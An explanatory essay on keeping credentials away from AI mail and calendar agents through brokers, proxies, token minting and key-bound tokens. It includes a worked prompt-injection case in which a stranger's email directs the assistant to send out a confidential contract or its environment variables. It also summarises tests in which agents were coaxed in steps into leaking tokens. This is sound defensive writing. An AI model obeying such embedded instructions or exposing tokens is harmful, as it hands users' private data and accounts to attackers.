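# Privilege Separation and Credential Brokering for AI Agents That Use Email and Calendar APIs

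## What does an agent need in order to use someone's mail and calendar?

An AI agent for mail and calendars is a program in which a language model reads a person's messages and appointments and acts on them by answering, forwarding, declining or booking. It works through APIs, the interfaces that providers such as Google and Microsoft offer to software. An API releases private data only to a caller with a credential (a password, a key or a token), so some part of the system has to use the person's credential. Privilege separation and credential brokering are two ways to decide which part. Privilege separation divides a program so that the part exposed to untrusted input lacks the rights to do serious harm. Credential brokering applies the same idea to the credential by having a separate process, the broker, keep the real one while the agent works with a stand-in.

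"Credential surrogation" is a rare name for the same arrangement. Most sources call it brokering. Examples are *Credential Brokering for AI Agents, Explained*, an introduction by the software vendor Infisical, and Hartman's *Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)* (2026), an informational draft posted with the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes the internet's technical standards. The survey *AI Identity* (2026) uses a third name, "token vault".

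### One request, from sentence to API call

Suppose Dana gets more meeting requests than she can handle and types to her assistant, "Answer this week's meeting requests and book them."

The harness, the ordinary software around the language model, combines her sentence with the developer's standing instructions and a list of tools. A tool is a function the harness can run, such as searching the mailbox, reading a message, sending a message, listing events or creating an event. The harness sends all of this as one text to the planner, the language model that selects the next call and its values. The planner can only produce text and cannot open a network connection. Here, its output is a short structured proposal to run the mail search with this week's dates.

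The harness parses the proposal. The tool's code builds a web request to the mail API, attaches Dana's credential and sends the request. The API returns messages, and the harness appends them to the text so far and sends all of it back to the planner, which proposes the next call. This loop repeats until the planner writes a final answer for Dana instead of proposing another call.

Many agents also have a sandbox, an environment for running code that is closed off from the rest of the system. If a script is the easiest way to compare the free hours of nine colleagues, the planner writes it and the harness runs it in the sandbox. *Scaling Managed Agents*, Anthropic's engineering post about its hosted agent service, similarly divides an agent into a harness, a sandbox and a session. The harness is the loop that calls the model, Claude, and routes its tool calls. The sandbox is where Claude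 runs code and edits files, and the session is an append-only log of everything that happened.

To handle Dana's request, the agent needs the credential only when it sends a web request to the API. The planner has to know that it can search mail and which dates to ask for, but it doesn't need to hold the credential. Many agents still put the credential where the planner can access it. How risky this is depends on the type of credential.

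### What OAuth gives the application

The crudest method is for Dana to give the agent her password. NIST, the US standards institute, notes that giving agents personal and work credentials has quickly become common, although security professionals have warned against sharing passwords for as long as passwords have existed. Sharing a password removes accountability because the service can no longer distinguish Dana's actions from the agent's.

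OAuth 2.0 is the usual alternative. Hardt (2012), in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework*, defined it as a way for a third-party application to obtain limited access to a service with the owner's approval. For an application that runs on a web server, the guide that Google publishes for developers sets out roughly this sequence:

1. The developer registers the assistant with Google and receives a client ID and a client secret. These identify the application and have nothing to do with Dana.
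2. The assistant sends Dana's browser to a Google page. She logs in there, so her password never reaches the assistant, and Google asks her which of the requested permissions she will grant. Each permission has a label, called a scope.
3. If she agrees, Google returns an authorization code, and the application exchanges the code for an access token and a refresh token.
4. The application puts the access token into a header of every request it sends to the API.
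5. When the access token expires, the application uses the refresh token to get a new one without asking Dana again.

The two tokens have very different lifetimes. In a sample response in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework: Bearer Token Usage* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), the access token lasts one hour and the refresh token has no stated expiry. In practice, a refresh token lasts until something ends it, such as a user's decision or an administrator's policy, so losing one is usually more serious than losing an access token.

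Both documents date from 2012, and *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security* has since updated their security advice and deprecated some of the less secure ways of using OAuth. But the plain access token is still a bearer token, which Jones and Hardt define as one that anyone who has it can use in the same ways as anyone else who has it. A request carries a line such as `Authorization: Bearer mF_9.B5f-4.1JqM`, and the API checks that the token is valid and covers the operation. The sender doesn't have to prove who they are, so the result is the same whether the request came from Dana's assistant, a script the assistant wrote or a stranger's laptop.

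*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) makes the same observation about static API keys, the long-lived strings that many services issue instead of OAuth tokens: the service cannot tell the intended agent from a compromised one. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) is more critical, describing the credentials agents hold today as "ambient, exportable, broadly scoped bearer secrets", though it is also arguing for its own proposal, hardware-bound credentials. "Ambient" means that any code running in the right place can use the secret without being given it for that purpose.

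OAuth also fits agents awkwardly because its designers assumed a human user behind the application. According to *AI Identity*, developers who apply it to agents unchanged end up either letting the agent replay the user's own token, which amounts to impersonation, or falling back on broad static keys. Both make it harder to tell from the records who did what.

### Where the token ends up in a naive agent

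The quickest way for a developer to let the planner call an API is to paste the credential into the prompt, next to the instructions. Users also paste keys into the chat window. In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), who work for the credential vault vendor Corvic, trace how the key is then copied into the model's context, the conversation history, execution logs, memory stores, generated code and error messages. They argue that a single paste creates several durable copies in systems built for retention and retrieval, which makes it hard to tell how far the secret has spread. The harness also resends the context at each turn of the loop, so the planner has the key in its input every time it writes anything.

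A more careful developer puts the secret in an environment variable, a named value that the operating system gives a process when it starts. This keeps the secret out of the prompt and the source code, but a process normally passes its environment to every process it launches. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026), a paper on coding agents, describes child processes that receive cloud keys and model-provider keys because the harness didn't remove them before starting those processes. If the planner can run code, it can print every variable with one line of script.

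Anthropic reports that its own service began with a version of this flaw. The code Claude generated ran in the same container as the credentials, so an attacker could get the tokens just by persuading Claude to read its own environment. The attacker could then start new, unrestricted sessions and delegate work to them. Narrower tokens would have limited the damage, but Anthropic's engineers did not want to rely on that alone, because it meant assuming there were things a model couldn't do with a limited token, even as models kept improving.

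Tokens can also end up in logs, which are perhaps the easiest place to forget. Anthropic's *The evolution of agentic surfaces* describes the session log as holding every model call, tool call and result, which lets a developer reconstruct a whole run. If the planner passes a token as an argument to a tool, the token will therefore stay in the log for as long as the log exists. OAuth also allows an application to put the token in the web address of a request instead of in a header. Google advises against this, as do Jones and Hardt, because servers tend to log addresses.

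Generated code can also leak credentials. A planner with a key in its context can easily write that key into a script, and the script may end up in a shared repository. GitGuardian, a company that scans for such leaks, counted about 23.8 million hardcoded secrets in public GitHub commits made during 2024, a quarter more than the year before. Kenney and colleagues, who cite the figure, rightly treat it with caution because it depends on one vendor's detectors and a detected secret may no longer have worked. The count also covers everyone's secrets, not just those that agents leaked. It does show that credentials were already leaking through code before agents began writing so much of it.

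The harm from a leak depends on which credential leaked. An access token that expires after an hour is useless in last month's log, but a refresh token or a static key in the same log may still open the mailbox.

### Text from strangers

An attacker can exploit these leaks just by finding a copy. In prompt injection, the attacker takes a more active part by placing text in material the planner reads, and the planner follows that text as if it were an instruction from the user.

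The weakness comes from the agent's loop. *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (2025) explains that at each step the agent gives the model its entire context, including untrusted data, and any part of that input can influence the output. The developer's instructions, Dana's sentence and the body of a stranger's email all reach the planner through the same channel. Training makes a model more likely to follow the first two than the third, but doesn't guarantee that it will. If an attacker's text sways the planner, the attacker can use any tool the planner has.

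Researchers distinguish direct prompt injection, in which the person typing tries to override the developer's instructions, from indirect prompt injection, in which the injected text is in a document or web page that the agent retrieves. The indirect form is the one that matters for mail, and Greshake and colleagues demonstrated it against real applications. Kenney and colleagues judged in September 2026 that no published defense fully prevents it.

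A mailbox is highly exposed to untrusted text because anyone who knows or guesses the address can send mail to it, and the agent's job is to read that mail. Strangers can also put text into a calendar, since the sender of an invitation chooses its title, location and description. Depending on the owner's settings, the invitation may appear in the calendar before the owner has responded. An agent looking for a free half hour on Thursday may therefore read a stranger's words without opening an email. A company can forbid an agent to visit unknown websites, but it can't so easily forbid the agent to read mail from unknown senders, because some meeting requests come from people the owner has never met.

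One of this week's messages is from such a person, who asks for half an hour on Thursday. Further down is a paragraph instructing the assistant to find a confidential contract in Dana's mailbox and send it to an outside address before confirming the meeting.

The harness fetches this message along with the others and appends it to the context. If the planner follows the paragraph, it will propose a search for the contract and then a message to the outside address with the contract attached. Dana's own request also requires the assistant to search her mail and write to people outside her company. The harness runs the calls, and the API finds a valid token on each and sends the contract to the outside address.

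The stranger could instead have asked the assistant to print its environment variables and email him the result. If the assistant kept its token there, he would then have the token.

### OpenSSH and the key that the child never holds

Programmers had to protect secrets inside programs that accept input from strangers long before language models existed. Provos, Friedl and Honeyman (2003) describe in *Preventing Privilege Escalation* how they did this in OpenSSH, which lets people log in to remote Unix machines. The OpenSSH server has to process data from anyone on the internet before it has identified them. It used to do all of this with superuser rights, so a programming error almost anywhere in it could give a remote stranger control of the whole machine.

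The design splits the server into two processes. An unprivileged child handles all the network traffic. Until a user logs in, it runs under an otherwise unused user ID, with an empty directory as its file system. A privileged parent, called the monitor, checks each of the child's requests and carries out those it permits. The permitted requests depend on how far the login has progressed. Some are valid only once, and if the child makes a request that isn't valid at that point, the monitor shuts down.

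Designers of agents have borrowed their treatment of the server's private key. The server must sign some data with this key to prove its identity. The child can ask the monitor for a signature, but no request returns the key itself. An attacker who takes complete control of the child can therefore get signatures but not the key.

To separate OpenSSH's privileges, Provos and colleagues changed about 950 of its 44,000 existing lines and added about 3,000. Login times barely changed (0.777 seconds against 0.775 with compression on). Afterwards, some two thirds of the code, including libraries, ran without privilege. If programming errors are spread evenly, two thirds of future ones would give an attacker no extra rights, though Provos and colleagues call this a back-of-the-envelope estimate. The old bugs they reviewed are better evidence, because the separation would have confined them. These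 included an integer overflow in packet handling and a flaw in the zlib compression library that no audit of OpenSSH's own code could have found. The separation also confined some holes that nobody knew about when they wrote it.

The planner in Dana's assistant corresponds closely to OpenSSH's exposed child, since it reads what strangers send, and a broker with her token would correspond to the monitor. But after a successful login, the OpenSSH child takes on the rights of the user who logged in. Provos and colleagues acknowledge that an adversary who controls the child can then run any command as that user. They accepted this risk because the server has identified the user by then. Dana's assistant acts with her rights from the start, while it is still reading mail from people it cannot identify.

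### Hardy's compiler

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an older program in that position, a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler was stored in a directory called SYSX and kept a file of usage statistics there, so the operators had given it permission to write files in that directory. Users could also tell the compiler where to write optional debugging output. One user gave the name of the file in SYSX that held the billing records. The operating system opened the file because the compiler had permission to write there, and the compiler overwrote the billing records with debugging output.

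The user never acquired the compiler's license. He only supplied a file name, and the compiler wrote to that file using its own authority. Hardy considers the obvious repairs and finds none satisfactory. The compiler could refuse any output file in SYSX, but some users might have a legitimate reason to write there. It could refuse that one file name, but there were other sensitive files, and more would come. Tymshare did add a system call that let a program state which of its two authorities it was using, but some programs soon needed more than two.

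He attributes the problem to the compiler holding authority from two parties with no way to keep the two apart. His remedy is the capability, a single object that both identifies a file and carries the right to write to it. The user supplies a capability for the output file instead of typing its name, and a user with no right to the billing records cannot supply one for them.

Several writers have applied the idea of the confused deputy, a program that serves two masters, to agents. In *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture*, the two masters are the person who installed the agent and whichever document or tool description the agent last retrieved. SANS, a security training organization, describes enterprise agents as the newest and potentially the most dangerous confused deputies in a company's cloud systems.

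I think the comparison holds only up to a point, and the differences make the agent's situation worse. Tymshare's user was a customer entitled to run the compiler, while the stranger who writes to Dana has no standing to ask her assistant for anything beyond a meeting. Hardy could also identify where the user's file name entered the program, but a planner processes Dana's sentence and the stranger's paragraph in the same computation, and the call it proposes has no label showing which of them prompted it. For Hardy's remedy to work here, something outside the planner would have to determine what Dana's request entitles the assistant to do, without trusting what the stranger wrote.

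### Theft and misuse

Dana therefore risks both theft of the credential and misuse of a permitted call. The two are easy to confuse because an attacker can attempt either with a malicious email.

A thief with the token can use it from his own machine, even when Dana's assistant is switched off. He can perform every operation the token's scope allows, including ones the harness never offered as a tool, until the token expires or someone revokes it. In misuse, the attacker never sees the token. Dana's harness makes calls for him, using its own tools, while his text influences the planner. Misuse gives him less power than theft, but it is harder to detect because the log shows ordinary tool calls made with a valid credential by the expected program.

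Both dangers can arise without prompt injection. Someone can find a token in an old log, and a planner can send the wrong file to the wrong person by mistake, which is why Kenney and colleagues list both ordinary model error and injection among the triggers for harm.

The defenses also differ. If no reusable credential enters the planner's context or the environment where its code runs, most of the places that might have held a copy never receive one, and Kenney and colleagues regard that part of the problem as removable by construction. But they note that an agent with no secret can still carry out an authorized but destructive operation. Tying a token to a cryptographic key has the same limit. A stolen copy is of little use without the key, but *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* points out that control of the key does not prove that the model chose the tool for an authorized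 purpose. A broker could keep Dana's token safe and still attach it to the request that sends the contract.

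## How can an agent make an authenticated call without holding the credential?

A broker has to sit between the agent and the mail API so that it can add the token after the agent writes the request. Suppose Dana's assistant has found a free half hour on Thursday and needs to confirm it with Lee, a client. The planner proposes a call to the send-message tool with Lee's address, a subject line and a sentence of text. The tool's code builds a web request, which passes through the broker much as Infisical describes for Agent Vault, its open-source broker.

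### One message through a broker

Where Dana's access token would normally go, the tool's code puts a placeholder that it has read from its environment:

```
POST /v1/messages/send HTTP/1.1
Host: api.mail.example
Authorization: Bearer __dana_mail_token__
Content-Type: application/json

{"to": "lee@client.example",
 "subject": "Thursday",
 "text": "Thursday at 2 pm works for Dana."}
```

The environment also contains a setting, `HTTPS_PROXY`, that directs web software to send its requests to the broker instead of straight to the internet. The broker must first identify the calling agent, because it may hold tokens for many people. In Infisical's *Agent Proxy*, a broker built into the company's command-line tool, each agent logs in with its own machine identity. In ZenML's *Credential proxy*, a developer guide with runnable code, the agent presents a token that the system creates for that run.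 The agent therefore still holds a secret that an attacker could steal, but that secret only gives access to the broker. Infisical advises operators to keep the broker on a private network, because anyone who could reach a public one might use it to make authenticated calls.

Next, the broker compares the request's destination with its rules. It finds that Dana's mail token belongs to `api.mail.example`, decrypts the token and puts it in place of the placeholder:

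```
POST /v1/messages/send HTTP/1.1
Host: api.mail.example
Authorization: Bearer at-7Qm2xV9kLr4TzB
Content-Type: application/json

{"to": "lee@client.example",
 "subject": "Thursday",
 "text": "Thursday at 2 pm works for Dana."}
```

Only the `Authorization` line has changed. The broker forwards the request, and the mail API handles it like any other request from Dana's account. The reply, perhaps just a message number and the word "sent", comes back through the broker to the tool, and the harness adds it to the planner's context.

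The broker must also check where each request is going. If it swapped the placeholder for the real token in requests to any address, an attacker could have the assistant call the attacker's server and read the token there. According to *Authenticate with vaults*, Anthropic's documentation for credential storage in its hosted agent service, the developer attaches a list of allowed hosts to each credential. If the sandbox sends the placeholder to any other host, that host receives it unchanged. Anthropic also offers an unrestricted setting for developers who can't list the hosts in advance, but strongly recommends a list.

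A careful broker would also check replies for secrets, because a service might repeat the request's headers in an error message or issue a new token in its answer. Hartman lists response filtering as a strength of brokers on the network path, but not every broker does it. Anthropic warns that its substitution works only on outbound traffic, so a token in a reply reaches the sandbox unredacted.

A developer can watch most of this happen in ZenML's example, where an agent in one container requests a page from a mock private wiki and a proxy in a second container adds the token. The logs show the request leaving the agent without an `Authorization` header and reaching the wiki with one. Searching the agent's environment for the wiki token finds nothing, and the wiki rejects requests that bypass the proxy. The example uses a dummy token and unencrypted traffic on a single machine, so it shows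 how the mechanism works but little about how well it would resist an attacker.

### Header or body

Some brokers skip the placeholder and set a header. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) shows how a few lines of the developer's code, running outside the sandbox, can add a token to every request for a given host. The code can also look up a different token for each sandbox. Vercel, a hosting company, has its firewall add the header and overwrite any header of the same name set by code in the sandbox. Otherwise, an attacker could supply a token for his own account at Dana's mail provider, and the assistant might save her documents in his mailbox.

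Infisical prefers placeholders because they show the broker where to put the key, whether in a header, the web address or somewhere else. A placeholder also works for programs that won't start without a key. Anthropic names two kinds of program for which it fails. Some check the key's format at startup and reject the placeholder. Others never send the secret and instead use it to sign the request, as Amazon's cloud services require. A signature computed from the placeholder is wrong, and the broker can't fix it by swapping a string.

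Replacing the placeholder wherever it appears is also riskier for mail than for most services. In the earlier example, a stranger asks the assistant to email him its environment variables. The assistant's message contains only `__dana_mail_token__`, but it is sent through the mail API, which is an allowed destination. If the broker replaces placeholders in the request body as well as the headers, it will insert Dana's real token into the message, and the mail API will deliver it to the stranger. Some mail APIs require the message to be encoded, which would keep the broker from recognizing the placeholder, but developers shouldn't rely on that.

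Anthropic lets developers limit credential substitution to request headers. It calls the body the broader exposure because agents often build request bodies from the content they are working on. By default, substitution happens in both places, which is the wrong setting for a mail credential.

Even with headers only, a rule that checks just the host is loose. ZenML points out that any request to an allowed host carries the token, whatever its path or method. If the token permits both, code in the sandbox could therefore delete Dana's messages as well as send one. The guide recommends restricting paths and methods too.

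### Reading encrypted traffic

Mail APIs use HTTPS, which encrypts each request between the client and the server. An ordinary proxy can forward the encrypted bytes but can't read or change the `Authorization` header. To change it, the broker must first decrypt the request, which requires the sandbox to accept the broker as if it were the mail API.

A server proves its identity with a certificate, a signed statement that a particular cryptographic key belongs to a particular host name. A certificate authority signs the statement, and every computer keeps a list of authorities it trusts. A broker with its own certificate authority can therefore impersonate any website to a sandbox that trusts that authority.

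Cloudflare's system creates a certificate authority with its own private key for each sandbox and places the authority's certificate inside. When the assistant opens a connection to `api.mail.example`, it sends that name before encryption begins. A separate network process next to the sandbox reads the name, produces a certificate for it and completes the connection in the mail API's place. The process then reads the request and passes it to the developer's code, which adds the token and forwards the request to the real API. According to Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026), the private key never leaves that process, and no two sandboxes share one. Anyone who stole a sandbox's key could impersonate websites to that sandbox, but a key shared by all customers would expose all their sandboxes.

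Programs inside the sandbox still have to trust the new certificate authority. According to Cloudflare's documentation, its sandbox makes a best effort to set this up for common tools such as Git, curl and Python's web library. A program with its own built-in list of authorities may still refuse the connection. The interception also covers only ports 80 and 443, the standard web ports. The older mail protocols, IMAP and SMTP, use other ports, so an assistant that reads and sends mail through them would get no token from this kind of broker.

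Interception also reduces Dana's privacy. The broker can read every message that the assistant fetches or sends for her, so she has to trust whoever operates it with those messages as well as her token.

### Naming a connector

The agent doesn't have to write the web request at all. It can name a connector, a service that the developer has set up in advance, and leave the request to software outside the sandbox. The planner's proposal for the message to Lee might then look like this:

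```
{"connector": "dana-mail",
 "tool": "send_message",
 "arguments": {"to": "lee@client.example",
               "subject": "Thursday",
               "text": "Thursday at 2 pm works for Dana."}}
```

Anthropic's hosted service, Managed Agents, works this way for tools that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to outside tools. As Anthropic describes it, Claude's tool call goes to a dedicated proxy with a token that identifies the session. The proxy uses the token to find the right credentials in a vault, then calls the outside service itself. The harness never receives any credential. When the developer starts a session for Dana, he attaches her vault, and the proxy selects the credential in it by the MCP server's address.

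This arrangement removes several of the problems with placeholders. The planner has no placeholder to copy into a message. It also can't choose a different host, path or method, because the connector offers only the operations its developer wrote. The proxy can read the call without impersonating anyone. However, the arrangement is less flexible. If the connector has no operation for comparing nine calendars, a script in the sandbox can't create one that uses Dana's access.

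The token still goes to the server behind the connector. A mail provider or a third party may run that server. If a third party runs it, that party receives Dana's token with every call.

### Getting tokens and renewing them

A broker can only insert a token it has, and it usually needs Dana's consent to get one. Posta, in *Credential Injection Patterns for AI Agents*, describes how this works in agentgateway, a gateway his company sells in an enterprise version. The first time an agent calls a service the gateway has no token for, the gateway rejects the call and returns a web address. The user opens it in her browser and consents, and the gateway stores the access and refresh tokens under her identity and the name of the service. It adds the access token to all her later calls to that service.

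Renewal should also happen at the broker. If the assistant's own code used the refresh token, it would receive a new access token, which is a real credential. This is why Anthropic advises developers to carry out such exchanges themselves and put the result in the vault. For connector credentials, Anthropic will renew an expired access token if the developer has supplied the refresh token and the address to send it to. Nobody can change that address afterwards, so an attacker can't redirect the refresh token to their own server. If renewal fails permanently, the developer receives a notice and has to ask the user to authorize again.

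*Obtain OAuth 2.0 access token*, part of AWS's documentation for its agent credential service, AgentCore Identity, describes a similar division. The service keeps refresh tokens, which AWS says last about 30 days by default, and uses them to replace access tokens, which often expire within one or two hours. The developer has to request a refresh token from the provider, using the parameter `access_type=offline` for Google or the scope `offline_access` for Microsoft. The service can't detect whether a user has revoked a token at the provider, so it may return one that no longer works.

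Because a broker looks up the credential for the agent, an administrator can replace the credential without restarting the agent. Infisical claims that its proxy starts using a new value within a minute.

### Three models in Hartman's draft

Most of the brokers described so far withhold every real credential from the agent, but AgentCore Identity gives the agent's code a working access token. Hartman treats withholding every credential as one of three models and doesn't recommend it as the main one.

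In a *proxy gateway*, the broker receives each request from the agent, adds the credential, forwards the request to the service and returns the response. In *short-lived token minting*, the broker uses the long-lived credential to obtain a temporary token with a narrower scope and gives that token to the agent, which then calls the service directly. The token expires after seconds or minutes. In *credential wrapping with scheduled revocation*, the broker gives the agent the real long-lived credential and revokes it when the task ends or a time limit passes.

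| | Proxy gateway | Token minting | Credential wrapping |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the agent holds | No real credential | A real token for seconds to minutes | The long-lived credential, until revocation |
| Added delay | An extra network hop on every call | One exchange with the broker per token | None |
| What the service must support | Nothing special | Issuing short-lived tokens | Canceling a credential on request |
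| What a thief gets from the agent | No credential for the service | Access within the token's scope until it expires | Full access until revocation succeeds |

Hartman discourages credential wrapping except for old services that offer no alternative, because a credential stays valid indefinitely if its revocation fails. He recommends token minting wherever a service supports it. With minting, the agent calls the service directly, so the broker doesn't become a bottleneck, and the large cloud providers already issue temporary tokens in very large numbers. But the agent holds a real credential in memory. Hartman lists this as a weakness of the model, even though he introduces the broker as a way for agents never to hold one.

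Some of his objections to the proxy gateway look weaker compared with working systems. He rates its delay as high because every call makes two hops. Cloudflare runs its proxy on the same machine as the sandbox and describes the extra delay as extremely minimal, though it gives no measurements. Infisical also recommends placing the broker close to the agent, since an agent may make hundreds of calls in a row. But it warns against running the two as containers on one machine, because they would share an operating system kernel, and one flaw in the kernel would expose the credentials.

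A proxy that only sets a header needs little more than the header's name and the host. Hartman also argues that a proxy must be able to parse the format of every API it serves, which is true of a proxy that filters messages by content.

His third objection, that the proxy is a single point of failure, applies almost as much to token minting. Under his own rules, a broker that breaks down issues no new tokens, so an agent whose tokens last 60 seconds would stop working about a minute later.

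Posta argues that for most companies today the recommendation is backward and the proxy gateway should come first. A short-lived token is still a reusable secret inside a system that isn't trusted with secrets. Services such as GitHub, Slack and Salesforce also don't let a company's own login system issue tokens for them, so each user has to consent in a browser, and the resulting token then has to be stored somewhere. Posta has a product to promote, but both points are accurate.

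The case for the proxy gateway is even stronger for Dana's mail. A broker could use her refresh token to get an access token and hand that to her assistant, but the access token would usually last about an hour, far longer than Hartman's seconds or minutes. Once the assistant had it, the broker could not see or stop individual calls.

The draft has no official standing. Hartman submitted version 00 as an individual in March 2026, no working group of the Internet Engineering Task Force has taken it up, and it expired on 30 September 2026. He does not appear to have posted a version 01. Sweeney's *Credential Delegation for AI Agents* (2026), a separate draft that expires on 29 January 2027, covers some of the same ground. In *Your AI Agent Is an Easily Confused Deputy*, Hartman counts more than 20 individual submissions on agent identity and authorization. His three models are still useful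 as a classification.

### Deciding and delivering

Hartman also splits the broker into two components. The policy decision point decides whether an agent may have a credential but never touches any credential. The credential delivery point has access to the vault but makes no decisions.

In his example, an agent wants to post a summary to the #engineering channel in Slack. It first submits a signed request that identifies the agent and states the service, action, channel, scope, reason and a lifetime of 60 seconds. The decision point checks the agent's identity, compares the request with the administrator's policy and the agent's past behavior, and may refer it to a person. If the request is approved, the decision point signs an approval with an exact scope and lifetime. The delivery point accepts only signed approvals. It fetches the long-lived credential, uses it to obtain the temporary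 token, wipes the credential from its memory and gives the token to the agent.

Hartman forbids the decision point to consider the stated reason, which exists only to help investigators reconstruct an incident. This rule is sensible because an agent under an attacker's influence would write a persuasive reason, and a decision component that read it could be manipulated by the same kind of text that manipulated the planner.

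The division resembles the one in OpenSSH, where the exposed child could ask for a signature but never for the key. It limits what an attacker gains from each component, though not equally. An attacker who controls the decision point gets no credentials directly but can approve any request. If he also controls an agent, he can have the delivery point send that agent any token. Control of the delivery point is worse because that component handles the real credentials. Hartman rates this threat as critical and accepts that a credential must exist briefly in the component's memory while it obtains the token.

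Token minting can also let the agent do more than the broker approved. The decision point might approve one message to Lee, but the resulting token can be no narrower than the mail provider's scopes allow, and a token that permits sending generally permits sending to anyone. The assistant could use it to send the contract to the stranger, and the broker would not detect this because the message would not pass through it. A proxy gateway receives the message, so it could at least compare the recipient with the approval.

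Short-lived tokens limit what an attacker gains by stealing them, but they do much less against an attacker who keeps control of the agent and has it request more. In an example from Hartman's SANS article, an agent needs Amazon's monitoring service, a database, Jira and Slack, and asks the broker for each token only when it needs it. Hartman writes that an attacker who takes over while the agent is reading the monitoring data has one read-only token that expires in less than a minute, and can't move on to the other services because those credentials don't exist yet. But the agent can still ask for them. The draft itself includes the threat of a compromised agent that words its requests to win automatic approval.

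### Tokens bound to a key

Under token minting, someone could still copy the temporary token from the agent's memory and use it elsewhere until it expired. Hartman addresses this with DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), which the Internet Engineering Task Force published in 2023 as RFC 9449. DPoP ties the token to a cryptographic key, so a copied token is useless without the key.

The agent generates a private and public key pair and gives the public key to the broker when it asks for a token. The broker arranges for the token to be bound to that key. With each call, the agent sends the token and a small proof signed with the private key. The proof includes the request's method, address and time, so an eavesdropper can't reuse it for a call to a different address. The service checks the token and the signature, and confirms that the signing key matches the one bound to the token, so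 a thief who has only the token can't produce the signature needed to use it.

DPoP's weak point is where the agent keeps the private key. If the key is in the same memory as the token, an attacker who can read one can probably read the other, and Hartman acknowledges that taking both defeats the protection. DPoP works best against copies of the token that end up elsewhere, such as in a log file or an error report, because the private key would not normally be there.

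DPoP also works only if the server that issues the token binds it to the key and the service checks the proof on every call. If either doesn't, the token is an ordinary bearer token. Posta writes that GitHub's personal tokens, API keys and the great majority of OAuth tokens for online services have no such check. For those services, Hartman has the agent send its proof to a proxy, which verifies it and then adds the real credential, so a design that starts with token minting becomes a proxy gateway for many services.

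His draft is also inconsistent about whether DPoP is required. The security section makes it mandatory, but the feature list for a minimal deployment omits it, and it appears only at the next level. A minimal deployment would therefore give agents plain bearer tokens, although they would be short-lived.

### What companies have deployed

Most of the brokers that companies offer for agents are proxy gateways, according to the makers' own descriptions. The exception is AWS.

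| Design | What reaches the agent's side | Closest model |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic Managed Agents, connectors | The result of the tool call | Proxy gateway |
| Anthropic Managed Agents, environment variables | A placeholder | Proxy gateway |
| Cloudflare outbound Workers | No credential | Proxy gateway |
| Vercel Sandbox | No credential | Proxy gateway |
| Infisical Agent Proxy | No credential, or a placeholder | Proxy gateway |
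| AWS AgentCore Identity | The provider's access token | Token minting |

Outside this group, Alibaba Cloud's *Outbound request header transformation* describes a sandbox that also follows the proxy model and supports both header setting and placeholders. Companies also combine their products. *New in Claude Managed Agents* announced that customers could run Anthropic's agents with Vercel's sandboxes, where Vercel's firewall adds the credentials.

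Vercel claims that a compromised agent in its sandbox has nothing to exfiltrate. This is fair for the credentials the firewall adds, but the agent could still access Dana's mail and send it elsewhere.

Anthropic handles Git differently from its connectors. It uses a repository's access token to clone the repository into the sandbox at the start, and builds the token into the local Git configuration so that the agent can push and pull without handling the token. Anthropic says that tokens are never reachable from the sandbox, but it doesn't explain how this one stays hidden from code running there.

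AgentCore Identity protects the token in storage but then gives it to the agent. AWS's *Features of AgentCore Identity* describes an encrypted vault that releases a credential only to an agent that proves its identity. The agent's code names the provider and the scopes it needs, and the service runs the consent process if necessary and returns an access token. AWS's *get-resource-oauth2-token*, the command's reference page, confirms that the caller receives the token itself. The refresh token stays in the vault, as Hartman would want. But the access token is the provider's ordinary one, which lasts an hour or two, and the agent's calls with it don't go through the broker.

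That token doesn't necessarily reach the planner, because the service passes it to a function in the developer's code. What the developer does next determines whether the token stays out of the planner's context and the logs. In AWS's *Step 3*, a walkthrough from the product's preview period that obtains a token for Google Drive, the sample function does nothing with the token except print it.

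## How well does a broker keep credentials safe?

In an agent with no broker, the secrecy of a token may depend on whether someone can talk the model into revealing it.

Okta, a company that sells identity software, tested whether an attacker could steal a token through OpenClaw, an open-source agent that people use to manage their inboxes, among other things (Kirk and Daly, 2026, *Phishing the agent*). The test assumed that a user had given the agent, running on Claude Sonnet 4.6, full access to a computer, including Keychain, Apple's store for passwords and tokens. It also assumed that an attacker had taken over the Telegram account through which the user gave the agent orders. Models usually resist sending a token outright, so the attacker split the theft into steps that each looked acceptable, cleared the agent's memory partway through, and received an image of the token.

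Much of this attack depended on the hijacked account, which gave the attacker the user's authority. A broker would have stopped him from taking the token, but not from ordering the agent to read and forward mail.

Other tests exposed credentials with less effort. When asked for the refresh token of a test Gmail account, the agent supplied it, then warned that the token was now exposed and that the user should revoke it. An agent running on dolphin-mistral:7b, a model built without the usual restrictions, was told only to complete a web form. It put its whole store of passwords, keys and tokens into the email field.

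Kirk and Daly also saw agents based on Claude refuse such requests. They don't count attempts, so their tests show that these leaks happen but not how often. Okta also has products to sell, but Kirk and Daly's point that agents "can't expose secrets they were never given" holds whatever the failure rate is.

### Sixteen probes of one vault

Kenney and colleagues tested an agent that held no credentials. The credentials were in Corvic Security Vault, a connector-based broker that their own company makes. On 27 September 2026, they ran code in the platform's sandbox and searched for the credentials that the vault was supposed to keep out. One experiment used a connector to GitHub, and the other used a connector to FRED, the economic database of the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis.

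Each probe had an expected outcome, fixed in advance. A call to the connector's own host had to succeed, and calls to other hosts had to arrive without the credential. The first requirement matters because a sandbox with no internet connection would also keep the credential from reaching other hosts.

All 16 probes, across seven control domains, had the expected security outcome. GitHub accepted a call as authenticated although the code had supplied no credential. None of the sandbox's 20 environment variables matched patterns for secrets, and none of 12 well-known credential files existed. Three echo services, websites that send back whatever they receive, returned no token. OpenAI's API rejected a call for lack of authentication, so the vault had not sent the GitHub credential there. The code also couldn't reach the internal addresses where machines in Amazon's and Google's clouds can get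 their own credentials.

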